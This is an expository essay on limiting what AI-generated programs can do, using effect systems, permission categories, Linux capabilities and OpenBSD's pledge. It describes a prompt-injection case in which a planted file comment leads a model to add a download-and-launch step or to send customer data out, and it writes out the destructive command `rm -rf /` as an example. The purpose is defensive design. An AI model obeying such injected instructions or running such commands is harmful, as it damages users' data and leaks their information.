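# Permissions and effect types for limiting the side effects of AI-generated code

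## What it means to bound a program's side effects

A side effect is anything a program does besides computing its result, such as writing a file, deleting a folder or sending a request to another computer. Bounding a program's side effects means deciding in advance which kinds it may have, and stopping the program, before it starts or while it runs, if it would go beyond them. A phone does this when it blocks an app from using the camera until the owner agrees. Programming-language researchers have a separate tradition of doing this with types, the part of a language that catches, before the program runs, mistakes such as multiplying a date by a street name.

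AI models now write programs and often run them straight away, so someone has to decide what a program may do without reading it first. A short, fixed list of permissions is about the simplest way to do this.

An effect category is a named class of side effects that a system grants or refuses as a whole. The "network" category, for example, covers every request to every computer. The effect list is the complete, fixed set of categories that the system recognises. A small list might have four: reading files, writing files, using the network, and starting processes (launching other programs). A grant is the part of the list that a particular program may use. A program that converts photographs between formats would be granted only reading and writing files.

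That choice follows least privilege, the security rule that a program should have only the permissions its task needs. A list of broad categories can only approximate this rule. The photo converter needs to read photographs, but a "read files" permission also lets it read tax returns. Excess authority is the set of permitted operations that the task does not need.

A program can get its powers through ambient authority or through capabilities. Ambient authority is power that code has merely by running. An ordinary program on a laptop, for example, can open any file that its user can open. A capability is an unforgeable value that a program must hold to perform an operation on a resource. Whoever starts a photo converter could give it a single capability that opens the holiday folder. The converter could not then open the tax folder just by naming it.

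### One program to follow

Suppose a manager asks a model to add up last month's sales and report the total to the accounts department. The model writes this:

```
text  = read_file("sales.csv")
lines = split_lines(text)
total = 0
for line in lines:
    amount = to_number(last_column(line))
    total  = total + amount
message = "Total sales: " + to_text(total)
reply = post(ACCOUNTS_ADDRESS, message)
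if reply != "ok":
    stop_with_error("total not delivered")
```

The first line reads a file. The eighth sends a message to a web address and waits for the reply, and both sending and receiving count as network use. The lines between them handle text and numbers in the program's own memory. So, of the four effects on the list, this program reads files and uses the network.

A program's effects are always relative to a list of what counts as an effect, so the sales program would have different effects under another list. *Lecture 26* (Park, 2026), from a course on programming language theory at Korea University, tracks four labels: exceptions, input and output, state, and non-termination. Under that list, the last line of the sales program has an effect because it can throw an error, while reading the file and posting the total both count as input and output. The list therefore doesn't distinguish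 a program that only reads the file from one that also sends something out. These labels work well for teaching how effects combine, but they would be a poor basis for deciding whether a stranger's program may use the network.

### The bound

Call the set of categories that the program may use when it runs E, and call the grant G. The program may run only when

E ⊆ G

which is to say, when every category in E is also in G. For the sales program E is {read files, use the network}. A grant of {read files} is too small, so the system refuses the program. A grant of exactly those two categories lets it run, and so does any larger one. Four categories make sixteen possible grants, counting the empty one, and four of the sixteen contain both of the categories in E. Least privilege picks the smallest of those four.

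To find E, the system needs to know which categories go with each basic operation. `read_file` carries "read files", `post` carries "use the network", and `to_number` carries nothing. E is the union of the categories of every operation the program might reach. If `to_number` actually writes a log to disk but isn't labelled "write files", E comes out too small and the condition above no longer gives protection. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a system for AI-written Scala code and makes avoiding such omissions an explicit requirement, called capability completeness: capabilities must regulate every effect that matters for safety, except those the system can contain at run time. The paper's main example of effects contained at run time is exceptions. Division by zero and exhausted memory can happen almost anywhere, so the system catches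 the resulting errors and turns them into ordinary values.

Suppose the model adds one more line to the sales program, which writes the raw text to a log file if a setting called `DEBUG` is on, and that `DEBUG` is always off. No run of the program will ever write a file, so the word "might" leaves it unclear whether E includes "write files".

It does. Lucassen (1987), in *Types and Effects*, a doctoral thesis at MIT, takes up the same case in its barest form, an expression that evaluates a condition and then one of two branches. Which branch runs depends on a value that nobody can in general know beforehand, and that may differ from one run to the next. Whether a program ever reaches a given line is undecidable, meaning that no procedure answers the question correctly for all programs. Lucassen therefore does not let an effect description depend on run-time values, and gives the whole expression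 a combination of the effects of both branches. In Park's notation, if the condition has effects ε₁ and the branches have ε₂ and ε₃, the conditional has

ε₁ ∪ ε₂ ∪ ε₃

The debugging line therefore adds "write files" to E, and the system rejects a harmless program because the grant allows only {read files, use the network}.

E is an upper estimate, as it must be for the bound to hold. If A is the set of categories that a run actually uses, a sound analysis guarantees that A ⊆ E for every run. Grossman (2012) states this guarantee in lecture notes on an effect system for exceptions: if a program raises an exception that nothing catches, that exception is in the set the system computed. When E ⊆ G as well, A ⊆ G, so every run stays within the grant. A run can also stay within the grant when E does not, because A may be far smaller than E. Grossman describes this conservatism, which comes from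 branching and error handling, as a feature of all effect systems.

Making E too small is a more serious error than making it too large, because it lets a program do something nobody allowed. When E is too large, the system rejects a safe program, and the model can usually delete the debugging line and try again. Overestimating is never unsound, as Park notes, so a designer in doubt about an operation should attach the category. But if safe programs fail the check often enough, the person in charge will be tempted to widen every grant until the refusals stop, and the bound will then still hold but restrict little.

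A program can meet the condition and still be wrong. If the last column of the file holds the tax on each sale, the program has the right effects but sends the accounts department the wrong total. A program that posted zero every month would also pass. The condition also doesn't depend on which file or address the program uses. If the program read the payroll instead of `sales.csv` and posted to a stranger's server instead of the accounts department, E would be the same. A scope, which is a limit attached to a category, such as one folder or one host, can prevent some of these substitutions. But a set of permitted operations doesn't by itself determine information flow, which is where data goes after a program has read it.

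### Where effect systems came from

An effect system extends a type system to compute which effects an expression may have. The idea goes back to *Integrating Functional and Imperative Programming* (Gifford and Lucassen, 1986). Gifford and Lucassen wanted to combine functional and imperative code in one language, a goal that had little to do with security. Functional code has no side effects, so it is easy to reason about and to run on several processors. Imperative code changes state as it runs, and most practical programs need some of it. To support both, the compiler had to distinguish the functional parts of a program from the imperative ones.

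The thesis of the following year describes two optimizations that a compiler can make when it knows a program's effects. If neither of two expressions writes to memory that the other reads or writes, the compiler can run them at the same time. If a function doesn't read or write any changeable memory outside itself, the compiler can store its past results and reuse them. In the sales program, the compiler could do this for `to_number` but not for `post`, because each call to `post` must send a message to the accounts department, even if the message is identical to an earlier one.

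The first effect system, designed in 1986, used what Lucassen describes as "a small, fixed set of effect classes". In Lucassen's thesis, an effect instead consists of a sort, such as reading, writing or allocating, and a region, which is a group of memory locations that the programmer marks out. The number of regions is unlimited. This made effects more precise, but Lucassen concedes that it also made declarations more of a burden to write, and hoped that compilers could take over much of that work by inference. Anyone who draws up a list of permissions today faces the same trade-off between precision and effort, and the effort falls on administrators and users as well as programmers.

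The other advance concerned functions that take functions as arguments. Suppose the sales program uses a general-purpose `for_each(lines, f)`, which applies `f` to every line. If `f` adds a number to the total, `for_each` has no outside effects. If `f` posts each line to a server, `for_each` uses the network. A single fixed description of `for_each` would have to list every category of effect, because `f` could have any of them, and every program that used it to loop over a list would appear to have them all. The thesis solves this with effect polymorphism, which lets the description of `for_each` read "whatever effects `f` has", and the system fills in those effects at each use. A year later, the idea gave Lucassen and Gifford's conference paper its title, *Polymorphic Effect Systems* (1988).

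A less famous step in Lucassen's thesis, turning effect estimates into checks, is more relevant to code from an untrusted author. Earlier compilers estimated effects by tracing which routine calls which, but this fails once programs can store routines in variables and pass them around. In Lucassen's approach, the programmer declares the effects of each routine, and the compiler works out the effects from the code and compares them with the declaration. The compiler rejects false declarations, so nobody has to trust them, whether a person or a language model wrote them.

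After forty years, effect systems have had modest success. According to *Type, Ability, and Effect Systems* (2025), very few of the many effect systems in the research literature have been used outside experimental settings. Java's checked exceptions were widely used, but many people regard them as a failed experiment because the extra type parameters seem to be more trouble than the checking is worth. Park counts more systems, including Haskell's way of marking input and output in types and even Rust's `async` and `unsafe` markers. The counts differ mostly because they define effect systems differently. The stricter count is more useful for someone who wants to bound side effects, since neither Java's exceptions nor Rust's markers distinguish a program that reads files from one that uses the network.

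### Code that nobody has read

All of this applies to programs that people write, but it is more pressing for generated programs, first because they often run before anyone has looked at them. Odersky and colleagues describe AI agents, systems in which a model takes actions through software tools, that write a short program combining several tools and run it in one step instead of calling the tools one by one. Citing earlier work but giving no figure, they add that tool calls often happen automatically and with little human oversight. They also note that coding agents often have access to an entire project directory, including passwords and access keys. This is a plain case of ambient authority, because the agent can read the keys simply because of where it runs, whether or not its task involves them.

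The second reason is that someone other than the user may influence the model that writes the program. Prompt injection is text in a model's input that makes the model follow someone else's instructions. The sales program can't follow instructions hidden in `sales.csv`, because it only processes the file as data; at worst, `to_number` fails. But a model may well open the file before it writes the program, to see which column holds the amounts. If a customer has typed into a comment field that the assistant should first download and launch a certain tool, the model may put that step into the code. The program would still produce the total the user asked for, so the user may not notice the extra step.

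A bound on effects limits what a fooled model can do, but doesn't keep the model from being fooled. Odersky and colleagues treat the model as a possible attacker, and any code it submits, for whatever reason, must pass the type checker. With the grant {read files, use the network}, the program that launches the downloaded tool fails the check, because "start processes" is in E and not in G. If the comment had instead asked for the customer list to be sent to an outside address, the program would have passed, because a legitimate sales program also reads files and uses the network. This weakness of short lists is hard to avoid with these two categories, because many useful programs both read and send data.

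There are three places to apply a list. The first is in types, where a compiler works out E from the program's text and rejects the program before it runs if E includes an effect that isn't on the list. The sales program with its debugging line would never start, and a program that passes needs no monitoring for the effects the types cover. The second is in run-time permissions, where the operating system or language runtime checks each operation as the program attempts it. This requires no estimate, so the unused debugging line does no harm, but a refusal can come halfway through. A sales program without the network permission would read the file, add everything up and fail at the eighth line, and a program that had already changed three files when it met a refusal would leave them changed. The third is in labels on tools, for agents that choose from ready-made operations. Whoever supplies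 `post` labels it "use the network", and the system offers it only to agents whose grant includes that category.

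## Drawing up the list of effect categories

Types, run-time permissions and tool labels can only enforce a list of effect categories that somebody has written. A sensible order for writing one is to list the harms to prevent, list every basic operation that a program can reach, put each operation into exactly one category, check for operations with no category and for a category with too many operations, and then try the list on sample tasks. Names like "files" and "network" are a poor starting point because they sound complete but leave most of the decisions open. Whether "files" includes deleting a folder, or "network" includes paying an invoice, depends on which operations someone put in that category.

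### Harms and operations

The manager who runs the sales program might worry that it will leak the sales figures to an outsider, destroy last month's records, launch other software, or run up a bill. For each of these harms, the list needs at least one category that the manager can refuse to prevent the harm or make it harder to cause. A category that helps against none of these harms is probably not worth having. The harms also depend on where the program runs. On a throwaway machine that holds only a copy of `sales.csv`, deleting files does no damage, and nearly all the danger comes from network access.

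Operations on the same kind of resource can cause quite different harms. *SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (2026), a benchmark of coding agents that go beyond their instructions, scores four file operations separately. It treats creating unrequested files as a problem of hygiene and privacy, changing unrelated files as one of integrity and privacy, deleting files as one of safety and data loss, and reading more files than the task requires as one of privacy. This supports splitting "files" into several categories, but not conclusively, because each extra category in a grant requires another decision from a person, which an extra benchmark score does not. The benchmark also penalises an agent for failing to read a file it needed, a failure that no permission can prevent.

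The next step is to inventory every primitive operation, meaning one that the program can't build out of smaller operations the system already checks. In the sales program, `read_file` and `post` are primitives, but a function `send_report` that called both would not be. Primitives can be in the standard library, in libraries from other languages, and in the agent's tools.

A language that runs on an older platform inherits many operations whose effects must be recorded. Flix, a research language that runs on the Java platform, includes a database that assigns effects to the classes, constructors and methods of Java's standard library. A new language can keep its list of operations short enough for one person to check by hand. AILANG's *Effect System*, the reference page for a language that its makers present as AI-friendly, lists eleven built-in operations: three for the console (the text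 window where a program prints and reads typed input), three for files, two for the clock, two for the network, and one for reading environment variables, the named settings that a program receives when it starts.

### One category for each operation

If either of two categories permits an operation, refusing only one of them doesn't stop it. Linux, for example, divides the powers of the administrator account into named permissions. It calls them capabilities, although they are entries in a fixed list rather than unforgeable values that a program holds and passes on. According to the Linux man-pages' *capabilities(7)*, a program with either `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` or `CAP_SYS_RESOURCE` can override the limit on how many processes a user may run, so an administrator who wants to enforce that limit has to withhold both.

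Some operations seem to belong in two categories. Sailfin's *The Effect System*, a guide to a new language whose compiler checks declared effects, has an example function that looks up a user in a database and declares both `io` and `net`. If the compiler can analyze the database library's code, the designer doesn't have to choose a category for the query, because its effects are the union of the effects of the primitives it uses. If the compiler can't, the designer has to treat the query as a primitive. A separate "database" category then makes sense if some programs should be allowed to query the database but have no other network access.

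Copying a file is a more dangerous example. Flix's *FileSystem* puts copying under the `FileWrite` effect, together with writing, moving and deleting, but a copy also reads a file. A program with `FileWrite` but not `FileRead` could therefore copy the payroll into a folder that the whole office can open. Treating a copy as a read followed by a write prevents this, because the program then needs both permissions.

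Even when operations are sorted neatly into categories, the categories can overlap in what they let code do. A draft of Flix's manual describes the language's effects as "mostly disjoint, but not entirely". Code allowed to start other programs can use them to access files, and code allowed to read files may be able to reach a network drive that the computer presents as a folder. If a function lacks the effect for writing files, the guarantee is only that it can't write them through the ordinary Java operations.

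Starting processes is the most dangerous effect to permit. LWN, a news site about Linux, introduces effect systems with a Python function that computes a factorial but also passes the operating system the command `rm -rf /`, which tries to delete every file on the machine. The function only starts a process and never calls a delete operation itself. A designer should therefore treat "start processes" as permission to do almost anything, unless the system applies the same permissions to any program the code launches.

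### Contested categories

Language designers count reading a file as an effect, even though it leaves the file unchanged, because it makes results unpredictable. Flix's *Primitive Effects* points out that two reads of the same file may return different text, since the file may have changed in between. For permissions, a stronger reason is that a program can't leak a file it can't read. Some programs also need to read files but not write them. Linux has one capability that bypasses the permission checks on reading files and another that bypasses the checks on reading, writing and running them, so a backup program can hold the weaker one. Environment variables need the same care as files because they often hold passwords and access keys.

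A permission list can leave out reading, writing and allocating a program's own memory, because nobody needs to refuse a program permission to use its own variables. *Convenient Explicit Effects using Type Inference with Subeffects* (Tate and Leijen, 2010) treats the three as separate effects, but partly to help a compiler optimise.

A separate category for deletion would cover only one of the ways a program can lose data. It would still be useful, because many programs write files without needing to delete any, and a deletion can be hard to undo. But Flix can back up a file before each destructive operation, and its manual lists seven of these: three forms of `write`, `truncate`, `delete`, and the general forms of copy and move. A program that is refused `delete` could still lose data through the other six. The sales program, for example, could destroy its input with `write_file("sales.csv",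 "")`.

Separating operations that only add data from those that can overwrite or remove it protects files better than having a separate "delete" category, because a program denied "delete" can still wipe a file by overwriting it. The adding category would cover appending to a file, making a folder and creating a file under a new name. An append can still spoil a file, for example by adding false sales records, but the old lines survive. This division requires an operation that creates a file and fails if the name already exists, which a library may not have. A designer who can't add that operation would do better to keep a single "write files" category and make backups than to offer a separate "delete" category.

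Reading the clock or drawing a random number changes nothing outside the program and reveals little, but it can make the program behave differently from one run to the next. In *koka*, a set of slides on the language of that name, Leijen (2012) asks whether `f(e, e)` is the same as computing `e` once and using the result twice. It isn't if `e` reads the clock or flips a coin. This matters to anyone who tests a generated program before trusting it. A version of the sales program could post the right total until January and a wrong one afterwards, and every test in December would pass. Without a clock or random numbers, the program would have to do the same thing whenever it got the same input. Network access weakens this guarantee, because web servers normally include the date in their replies. For tests, AILANG can run a program with its clock fixed at a chosen time.

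"Clock" can cover different operations. In AILANG it includes both reading the time and sleeping (waiting for a set period), while Flix has a separate effect for each. Setting the clock affects every program on the machine, and Linux has a dedicated capability for it, `CAP_SYS_TIME`. On a short list, one category for the clock and random numbers together is probably enough. If nobody plans to repeat runs exactly, the category can be left out.

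Exceptions and non-termination should be listed separately from the effects that need permission. In Fox, the prototype language of Tate and Leijen, a function that may raise an exception is `partial`, one that may run forever is `divergent`, one that may do either is `pure`, and one that can do neither is `total`. The labels show which rewrites are safe. A compiler may replace `0 * x` with `0` only if computing `x` is sure to finish without an error. These labels would make poor permissions, because `to_number` can fail on a bad line of the sales file, and no manager would refuse the program for that. Ferrule, another language with effect declarations, separates control effects (failing, pausing and not returning) from resource effects (files, the network, the console, time and random numbers), and only resource effects need a capability. A time limit can stop a program that never ends,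 even when no compiler could have predicted the problem.

Spending money is hard to turn into a category because programs usually do it through a general-purpose operation. Paying an invoice and reporting the sales total can both be a `post` to a web address. A "spend" category works only if payments have their own operation and the program has no other way to reach the payment service. Even then, the amount matters more than the permission. The roadmap for AILANG includes budgets such as `IO @limit=2`, which attach a number to a category. If that number counts calls, it doesn't limit the total spent, because a single payment can be any size.

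Calling another AI model is often a network request, but some new languages give it a separate effect. Vera has both `<Inference>` and `<Http>`, so a function can have permission for either without the other. Model calls matter because they cost money, may send data to another company, and return text that may contain a prompt injection. But refusing them to a program with unrestricted network access achieves little, because the program can send the same request directly. The separate category is more useful for giving a program, such as one that summarises customer comments, permission to call the model and no other network access. A narrow category, whether for model calls, payments or databases, is worth adding when some programs can be given it instead of the broad category that contains it.

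### Gaps and catch-alls

The next check is for operations that have no category. A list with reading files, writing files, using the network and starting processes leaves out environment variables, clocks and random numbers. Refusing uncategorized operations is a better default than allowing them. If the system allows them, the sales program, with a grant for only files and the network, can read access keys from its environment variables and post them to a stranger. Refusing them makes some harmless programs fail, but each failure reveals a missing category. The designer can put operations judged harmless into an explicit "always allowed" group to distinguish them from forgotten ones.

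A language may also list an effect that its compiler doesn't check. Sailfin's *Effect System Reference* lists six effects: `io`, `net`, `model`, `gpu`, `rand` and `clock`. According to Sailfin's *§7 Effect System*, the compiler enforces only `io`, `net` and `clock`, while `model`, `gpu` and `rand` are reserved names with no detector yet. Sailfin's developers plan to add the detectors along with the libraries that use them, so this gap may do little harm for now. Neither page assigns starting a process or reading an environment variable to any of the six effects, and anyone who wanted to limit what generated code can do would need to decide how to classify both.

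Linux shows how a catch-all category forms. Each new privileged feature of the operating system needs some capability, and developers have attached a vast proportion of the checks to `CAP_SYS_ADMIN`. It lets a program mount disks, change the computer's name and administer many devices, among dozens of other things. Capabilities were supposed to divide the powers of root, the all-powerful administrator account, but the manual page says `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` could plausibly be called "the new root" because it confers a wide range of powers and many programs need it. Categories in other lists can be tested for the same two properties. A broad category that almost no program needs is much less of a problem, because administrators can refuse it.

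Linux developers have since split some powers off from `CAP_SYS_ADMIN`, including performance monitoring in version 5.8 and checkpointing (saving a running program so that it can resume later) in version 5.9. A program that needs only one of these can now hold a weaker capability. But `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` still permits the same operations, so programs that already hold it are no more restricted than before. A designer who separates the powers at the start avoids this problem.

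The same manual page advises kernel developers on where to put new features, and most of the advice also applies to effect categories. Developers should prefer an existing category to a new one, to keep the set manageable. A feature that is useless without certain others should share their category. A new category should be broad enough for related features to join later, and the page says that adding `CAP_SYS_PACCT`, which covers a single system call for process accounting, was probably a mistake. This is the judgement of people who maintained one list for a long time, and nobody tested it against alternatives. Reusing existing categories also has a drawback, since that is how `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` grew. The page therefore tells developers to avoid that capability if they possibly can, unless the new feature closely matches its existing uses.

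Some languages deliberately include a catch-all effect. In Sema's *Effects Catalog*, the marker `!{*}` stands for all effects and is meant for experiments. The checker warns about it at the lowest strictness level and rejects it at higher ones, and a reviewer can find every use with a text search. Fox's catch-all is `io`, which covers files, networking and any call to outside code. Tate and Leijen write that with `io`, "all bets are off". Fox's finer distinctions all concern memory, exceptions and termination. These suit their aim of helping programmers reason about code, but `io` doesn't distinguish a program that prints a greeting from one that erases the disk.

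### How grouping decides what anyone can refuse

Two operations in the same category always come together. No grant can permit one and refuse the other, however carefully someone chooses it. Sailfin and AILANG group a few ordinary operations differently:

| Operation | Sailfin | AILANG |
|---|---|---|
| Print to the console | `io` | `IO` |
| Read a file | `io` | `FS` |
| Write a file | `io` | `FS` |
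| Send a web request | `net` | `Net` |
| Sleep | `clock` | `Clock` |
| Read an environment variable | none listed | `Env` |

Sailfin's `io` lets a function read files, but AILANG's `IO` does not. In the introduction to Sailfin, the example function `greet` declares `io` because it prints a greeting. If a later version also read a file of passwords, the compiler would accept it with the same declaration. AILANG's reference page gives a similar function as an example of an error. It declares only `IO` but calls `readFile`, so it doesn't compile.

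Sailfin's `io` effect covers printing and logging as well as reading files. A dependency (a package of someone else's code that a program uses) that already has `io` because it prints or logs could start reading files without any change to its declared effects. Sailfin's developers promise that a dependency can't quietly start reading files without permission, but this holds only for packages without `io`. The developers plan to divide the broad effects into narrower ones, such as `io.fs` and `net.http`, which would fix this.

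AILANG has only eleven operations, so it is easy to count how many a grant permits unnecessarily. The sales program needs `readFile` and `httpPost`, so its grant is {`FS`, `Net`}, which permits five operations. The three it doesn't need are writing a file, checking whether a file exists, and fetching a web page. If AILANG put console and file operations into one category, as Sailfin does, the grant would permit eight operations, including six the program doesn't need. The three added operations print text or read typed input, and they add hardly any danger.

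The merger is much worse for a program that only prints. Under AILANG's own grouping, the program gets three console operations, two of which it doesn't need. With the groups merged, it gets six operations, including `writeFile`. So a mild operation that nearly every program needs should not share a category with a dangerous one that few need, because nearly every program would then get the dangerous one too.

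A longer list of categories doesn't always allow narrower permissions. Sailfin has six categories, more than the five on AILANG's page, yet it can't permit printing while refusing file access. Both languages put reading and writing files in the same category, so a sales program that is allowed to read `sales.csv` is also allowed to overwrite it. A slide deck on Flix lists separate `FsRead` and `FsWrite` effects, which make it possible to grant read access alone.

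### Counting excess authority

The excess authority of a grant can be calculated as the number of operations in all the categories it includes, minus the number the task needs. For illustration, an invented library has 40 operations: 8 read files, 8 write files, 10 use the network, 4 start or control processes, 4 deal with environment variables, 3 read the clock and 3 produce random numbers. The sales program needs 2 of them.

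With a single category, the grant permits all 40 operations. With three categories (files, network and the rest), the program needs files and network, so the grant permits 16 + 10 = 26. With seven, one for each kind of operation, the program needs file reading and network use, so the grant permits 8 + 10 = 18. With a category for every operation, the grant permits exactly 2.

More categories also mean more chances of a mistake. Suppose a programmer or a model declares a program's effects by answering yes or no for each category, and each answer independently has a 2% chance of being wrong. With *k* categories, the whole declaration is correct with probability 0.98ᵏ.

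| Categories | Operations permitted | Excess | Wholly correct declarations |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 40 | 38 | 98% |
| 3 | 26 | 24 | 94% |
| 7 | 18 | 16 | 87% |
| 40 | 2 | 0 | 45% |

For this program, all of the gain from using seven categories instead of three comes from separating reading files from writing them. A list of four categories (reading files, writing files, network and everything else) would also leave an excess of 16, and 92% of its declarations would be correct. Splitting the last category helps other programs. For example, a program that needs a single random number would be allowed 14 operations under the list of four, including starting processes, but only 3 under the list of seven. Choosing divisions that suit the programs at hand therefore matters more than the number of categories.

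The count treats all operations as equally harmful, which they aren't. Flix's file system has 29 operations, 3 of which read a file's contents, as one piece of text, as lines, or as bytes. A program that needs only one of these three has an excess of 28 if it is granted the whole file system, and an excess of 2 if it is granted only the three. Putting the three in their own category therefore removes 26 operations from the grant, including all 13 that write. Giving each operation its own category would remove the other 2, but they only read the same file in other formats, so removing them protects nothing. Much of the excess of 16 in the illustration may be of this kind. A designer could weight each operation by the harm it can do. The weights would be guesses, but even rough ones would put starting a process far above reading a clock.

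The 45% in the last row is also less alarming than it looks, because nearly all the extra mistakes on the longest list are unnecessary additions. A wrong declaration can leave out something the program needs, in which case the system refuses the program, or add something unnecessary, in which case the grant is too wide. The sales program needs two categories under the lists of three, seven and forty, so the chance that the declaration includes both is 96% for all three lists. On the list of 40, there are 38 operations that could be added by mistake, each with a 2% chance, so the average declaration includes 0.76 unnecessary operations. That is still far less excess than a perfect declaration grants under the list of 7.

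A long list of categories causes more refusals for larger programs. If a program needs 20 different operations, its declaration would include all of them only 67% of the time. The system would therefore refuse the program about one time in three, and people who see refusals that often are tempted to widen the grant.

Mistakes are unlikely to be independent either. An author who misunderstands how the network library works may get all ten of its operations wrong. If each answer is still wrong 2% of the time but mistakes can be correlated in any way, the share of correct declarations under the longest list could be anywhere from 20% to 98%. The error rate might also change with the length of the list. People may grow careless by the thirtieth question, but the questions on a longer list are narrower, and "does this program call `delete_file`?" is easier to answer than "does this program change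 the file system?"

A compiler can eliminate this kind of mistake by inferring the effects itself. In Fox, when a programmer adds a line that prints, the function's effect changes from `total` to `io` without any change to a declaration. In Sema, if the programmer leaves out the effects, the compiler infers the smallest set that fits the code. A long list of categories then adds almost no work for the person or model writing the program. But inference only finds what a program might do. The person who approves the grant still has to decide what the program should be allowed to do, and a long list gives that person more work. If the system simply copies the inferred effects into the grant, every program passes the check.

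### Trying the list on sample tasks

Twenty or thirty tasks of the kind the system will handle are a reasonable test of whether the list suits the actual work. For each task, the designer writes down the smallest sufficient grant and any authority it gives beyond what the task needs, then checks which of the original harms that grant would still allow. It helps to draw up the list from half of the tasks and keep the rest for the test, because otherwise the categories may fit only the examples that inspired them.

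If two categories appear together in every grant and guard against the same harm, the designer can merge them without losing anything. If nearly every task needs a category, people will soon grant it without thinking. The designer can then check whether many tasks need it only for a mild operation, such as printing, that is grouped with dangerous ones. A category that no task needs may still be one of the most valuable on the list. If none of the thirty tasks starts a process, denying them all "start processes" blocks nothing they need and removes the easiest way around the other categories.

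The trial should also include harmful programs. Under the seven-category list, a sales program allowed only to read files and use the network fails the check if it wipes `sales.csv` after posting the total, because it writes to a file. A program with the same permissions that posts the customers' names to a stranger still passes, as it did under the four-category list. Even 40 categories would not catch it, because sending the names and sending the total both use `post`.

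## How many categories programmers and administrators have managed

Programmers and system administrators have used permission lists for decades, and how well a list worked has not depended only on its length. OpenBSD's list has 32 usable categories, Linux's has 41 and Java's had 27. In one count, 86% of the processes on a running OpenBSD machine had used its list to limit their own permissions. On Linux, nearly half of the permission checks fell into one catch-all category. Java's maintainers switched their list off, partly because most of the few applications that used it granted themselves every permission at once.

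### OpenBSD's promises

OpenBSD is a free operating system known for its attention to security. A program running on it can limit itself by calling `pledge` with a string of keywords. Each keyword, called a promise, stands for a group of operations that the program may still use. The `echo` command, which only prints the words it receives, makes a very small call, reproduced by Hill, in *OpenBSD, pledge(), and unveil()*:

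```
pledge("stdio", NULL)
```

After this line, `echo` can print, but it can't open a document, connect to another computer or start a program. BCHS's *why pledge(2)*, from a project that promotes web applications written in C for BSD systems, gives a longer call from a working application:

```
pledge("stdio rpath cpath wpath flock fattr", NULL)
```

This program may also open files for reading (`rpath`) and writing (`wpath`), create and remove them (`cpath`), lock them (`flock`) and change details such as their timestamps (`fattr`). It needs these permissions because its database, SQLite, creates and changes files of its own.

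The sales program would need four promises: `stdio`, `rpath` to open `sales.csv`, `dns` to look up the accounts department's server by name, and `inet` to connect to it. If the program tries anything else, the kernel (the core of the operating system) kills it, and the program can't prevent this. If the debugging line is still there and somebody turns on `DEBUG`, the kernel kills the program when it tries to open the log. Where possible, the kernel saves a snapshot of the program's memory, which helps a developer find the missing promise.

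OpenBSD's *PLEDGE(2)* manual page, as of June 30, 2026, gives the number of groups as "approximately 3 dozen". It describes 33 promises, one of which, `tmppath`, no longer works. Another, `error`, permits nothing; it makes a forbidden operation return an error instead of killing the program. The kernel also accepts a few keywords that have no entries of their own in the manual. The software package *tesseras-paste 0.1.3*, whose source code copies the keywords from OpenBSD's kernel, has 36, including `disklabel`, `drm` and `vmm`.

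According to OpenBSD's *pledge*, an older version of the manual page, the designers chose the groups by studying the behavior of many existing programs. They could instead have made programmers list individual system calls, which are the requests a program makes to the kernel, such as opening a file or asking for the time. `stdio` alone covers about 70 system calls for low-risk operations that nearly every program needs, such as managing memory, using files that are already open, reading the clock and getting random numbers. Setting the clock, which is more dangerous than reading it, has its own promise, `settime`.

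Theo de Raadt, who leads OpenBSD, had looked at Linux's alternative, in which a programmer writes a small filter program to check system calls. An outside review of OpenBSD's defences, isopenbsdsecu.re, quotes him describing it as "insane" to write a program to observe a program. The reviewer agrees that a call that people can use is worth some loss of precision.

OpenBSD keeps the list manageable partly by handling awkward cases outside it. A program that prints the local time has to read the computer's time-zone file, but giving `rpath` to every such program would let them all read documents too. The kernel therefore lets OpenBSD's own C library open a few fixed system files even when the program has no file promise. OpenBSD has also withdrawn `tmppath`, a promise that gave programs access to the folder for temporary files. The manual now recommends either the ordinary file promises or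 `unveil`, a companion call that limits a program to chosen paths and so leaves little use for a category with one folder built in.

A program can call `pledge` again to give up more promises, but it can never get one back, so the order of its operations matters. `stdio` allows a program to keep using files and connections it has already opened. The sales program could open `sales.csv`, connect to the accounts department, and only then pledge `stdio` alone. After that it couldn't open the payroll or contact a stranger's server, although the other three promises would have let it do both. The programmer would first have to rewrite some of the code, because `post` connects and sends in a single step. In its slides, OpenBSD (2017) calls moving start-up work to the beginning "hoisting", and concedes that it depends on the "zeal of the developer". Larger programs often need more extensive changes.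 In *Privilege Separation and Pledge*, de Raadt describes splitting a program into several processes with different jobs, each of which can have its own short set of promises.

### Who took pledge up

On a running system, 86% of processes had used `pledge` and 39% had used `unveil`, according to slides by OpenBSD (2023). These figures count processes rather than programs, so a program running ten times counts ten times. Ruohonen, Sierszecki and Tiwari (2026), in *A Measurement Study on the Adoption of Pledges and Unveils*, followed OpenBSD's source code through 19 releases. OpenBSD's developers had already changed many programs before the two calls officially appeared, and adoption then rose roughly linearly. The developers also used nearly the whole range of promises. Ruohonen and colleagues conclude that adopting such restrictions needn't be as troublesome as the research literature often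 suggests.

By contrast, few packages outside OpenBSD's own code use `pledge`. Alhindi and Hallett (2024), in *Sandboxing Adoption in Open Source Ecosystems*, searched the C and C++ code of add-on packages for four operating systems. Of 7,700 packages for OpenBSD, 111 (1.4%) called `pledge`. Almost every call included `stdio`, and the next most common promises were `rpath`, `wpath` and `cpath`. No package used `mcast`, `tape`, `settime` or `error`.

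The promises are the same for basic programs and added packages, so their number can't explain the difference. OpenBSD's developers maintain the kernel, the C library and the basic programs together, so when a program doesn't fit the promises they can change either one. The author of an added package usually writes for several operating systems, and `pledge` works on only one of them. The gap between 86% and 1.4% overstates the effect because one figure is a share of processes and the other a share of packages, but it is too large for that to explain all of it.

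In both cases the program's own developers choose the promises. This protects against mistakes and against an attacker who takes over a legitimate program, but a program that is malicious from the start can leave out the call. The second argument of `pledge`, which is `NULL` in the two calls above, addresses this by setting the promises that any program started from the current one begins with. Whoever runs a generated sales program could start it from a small launcher that uses this argument to set the four promises, plus any that the language's own start-up needs. The generated program could then drop promises but not add any.

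Without that second argument, a program that is allowed to start others can escape its limits, because the new program starts with none. OpenBSD chose this deliberately because its command shell can't open network connections but has to start programs that can. The developers' slides say that Capsicum, FreeBSD's rival system, has no solution for this case. The choice suits a shell that OpenBSD wrote but would be a bad default for code that nobody has read.

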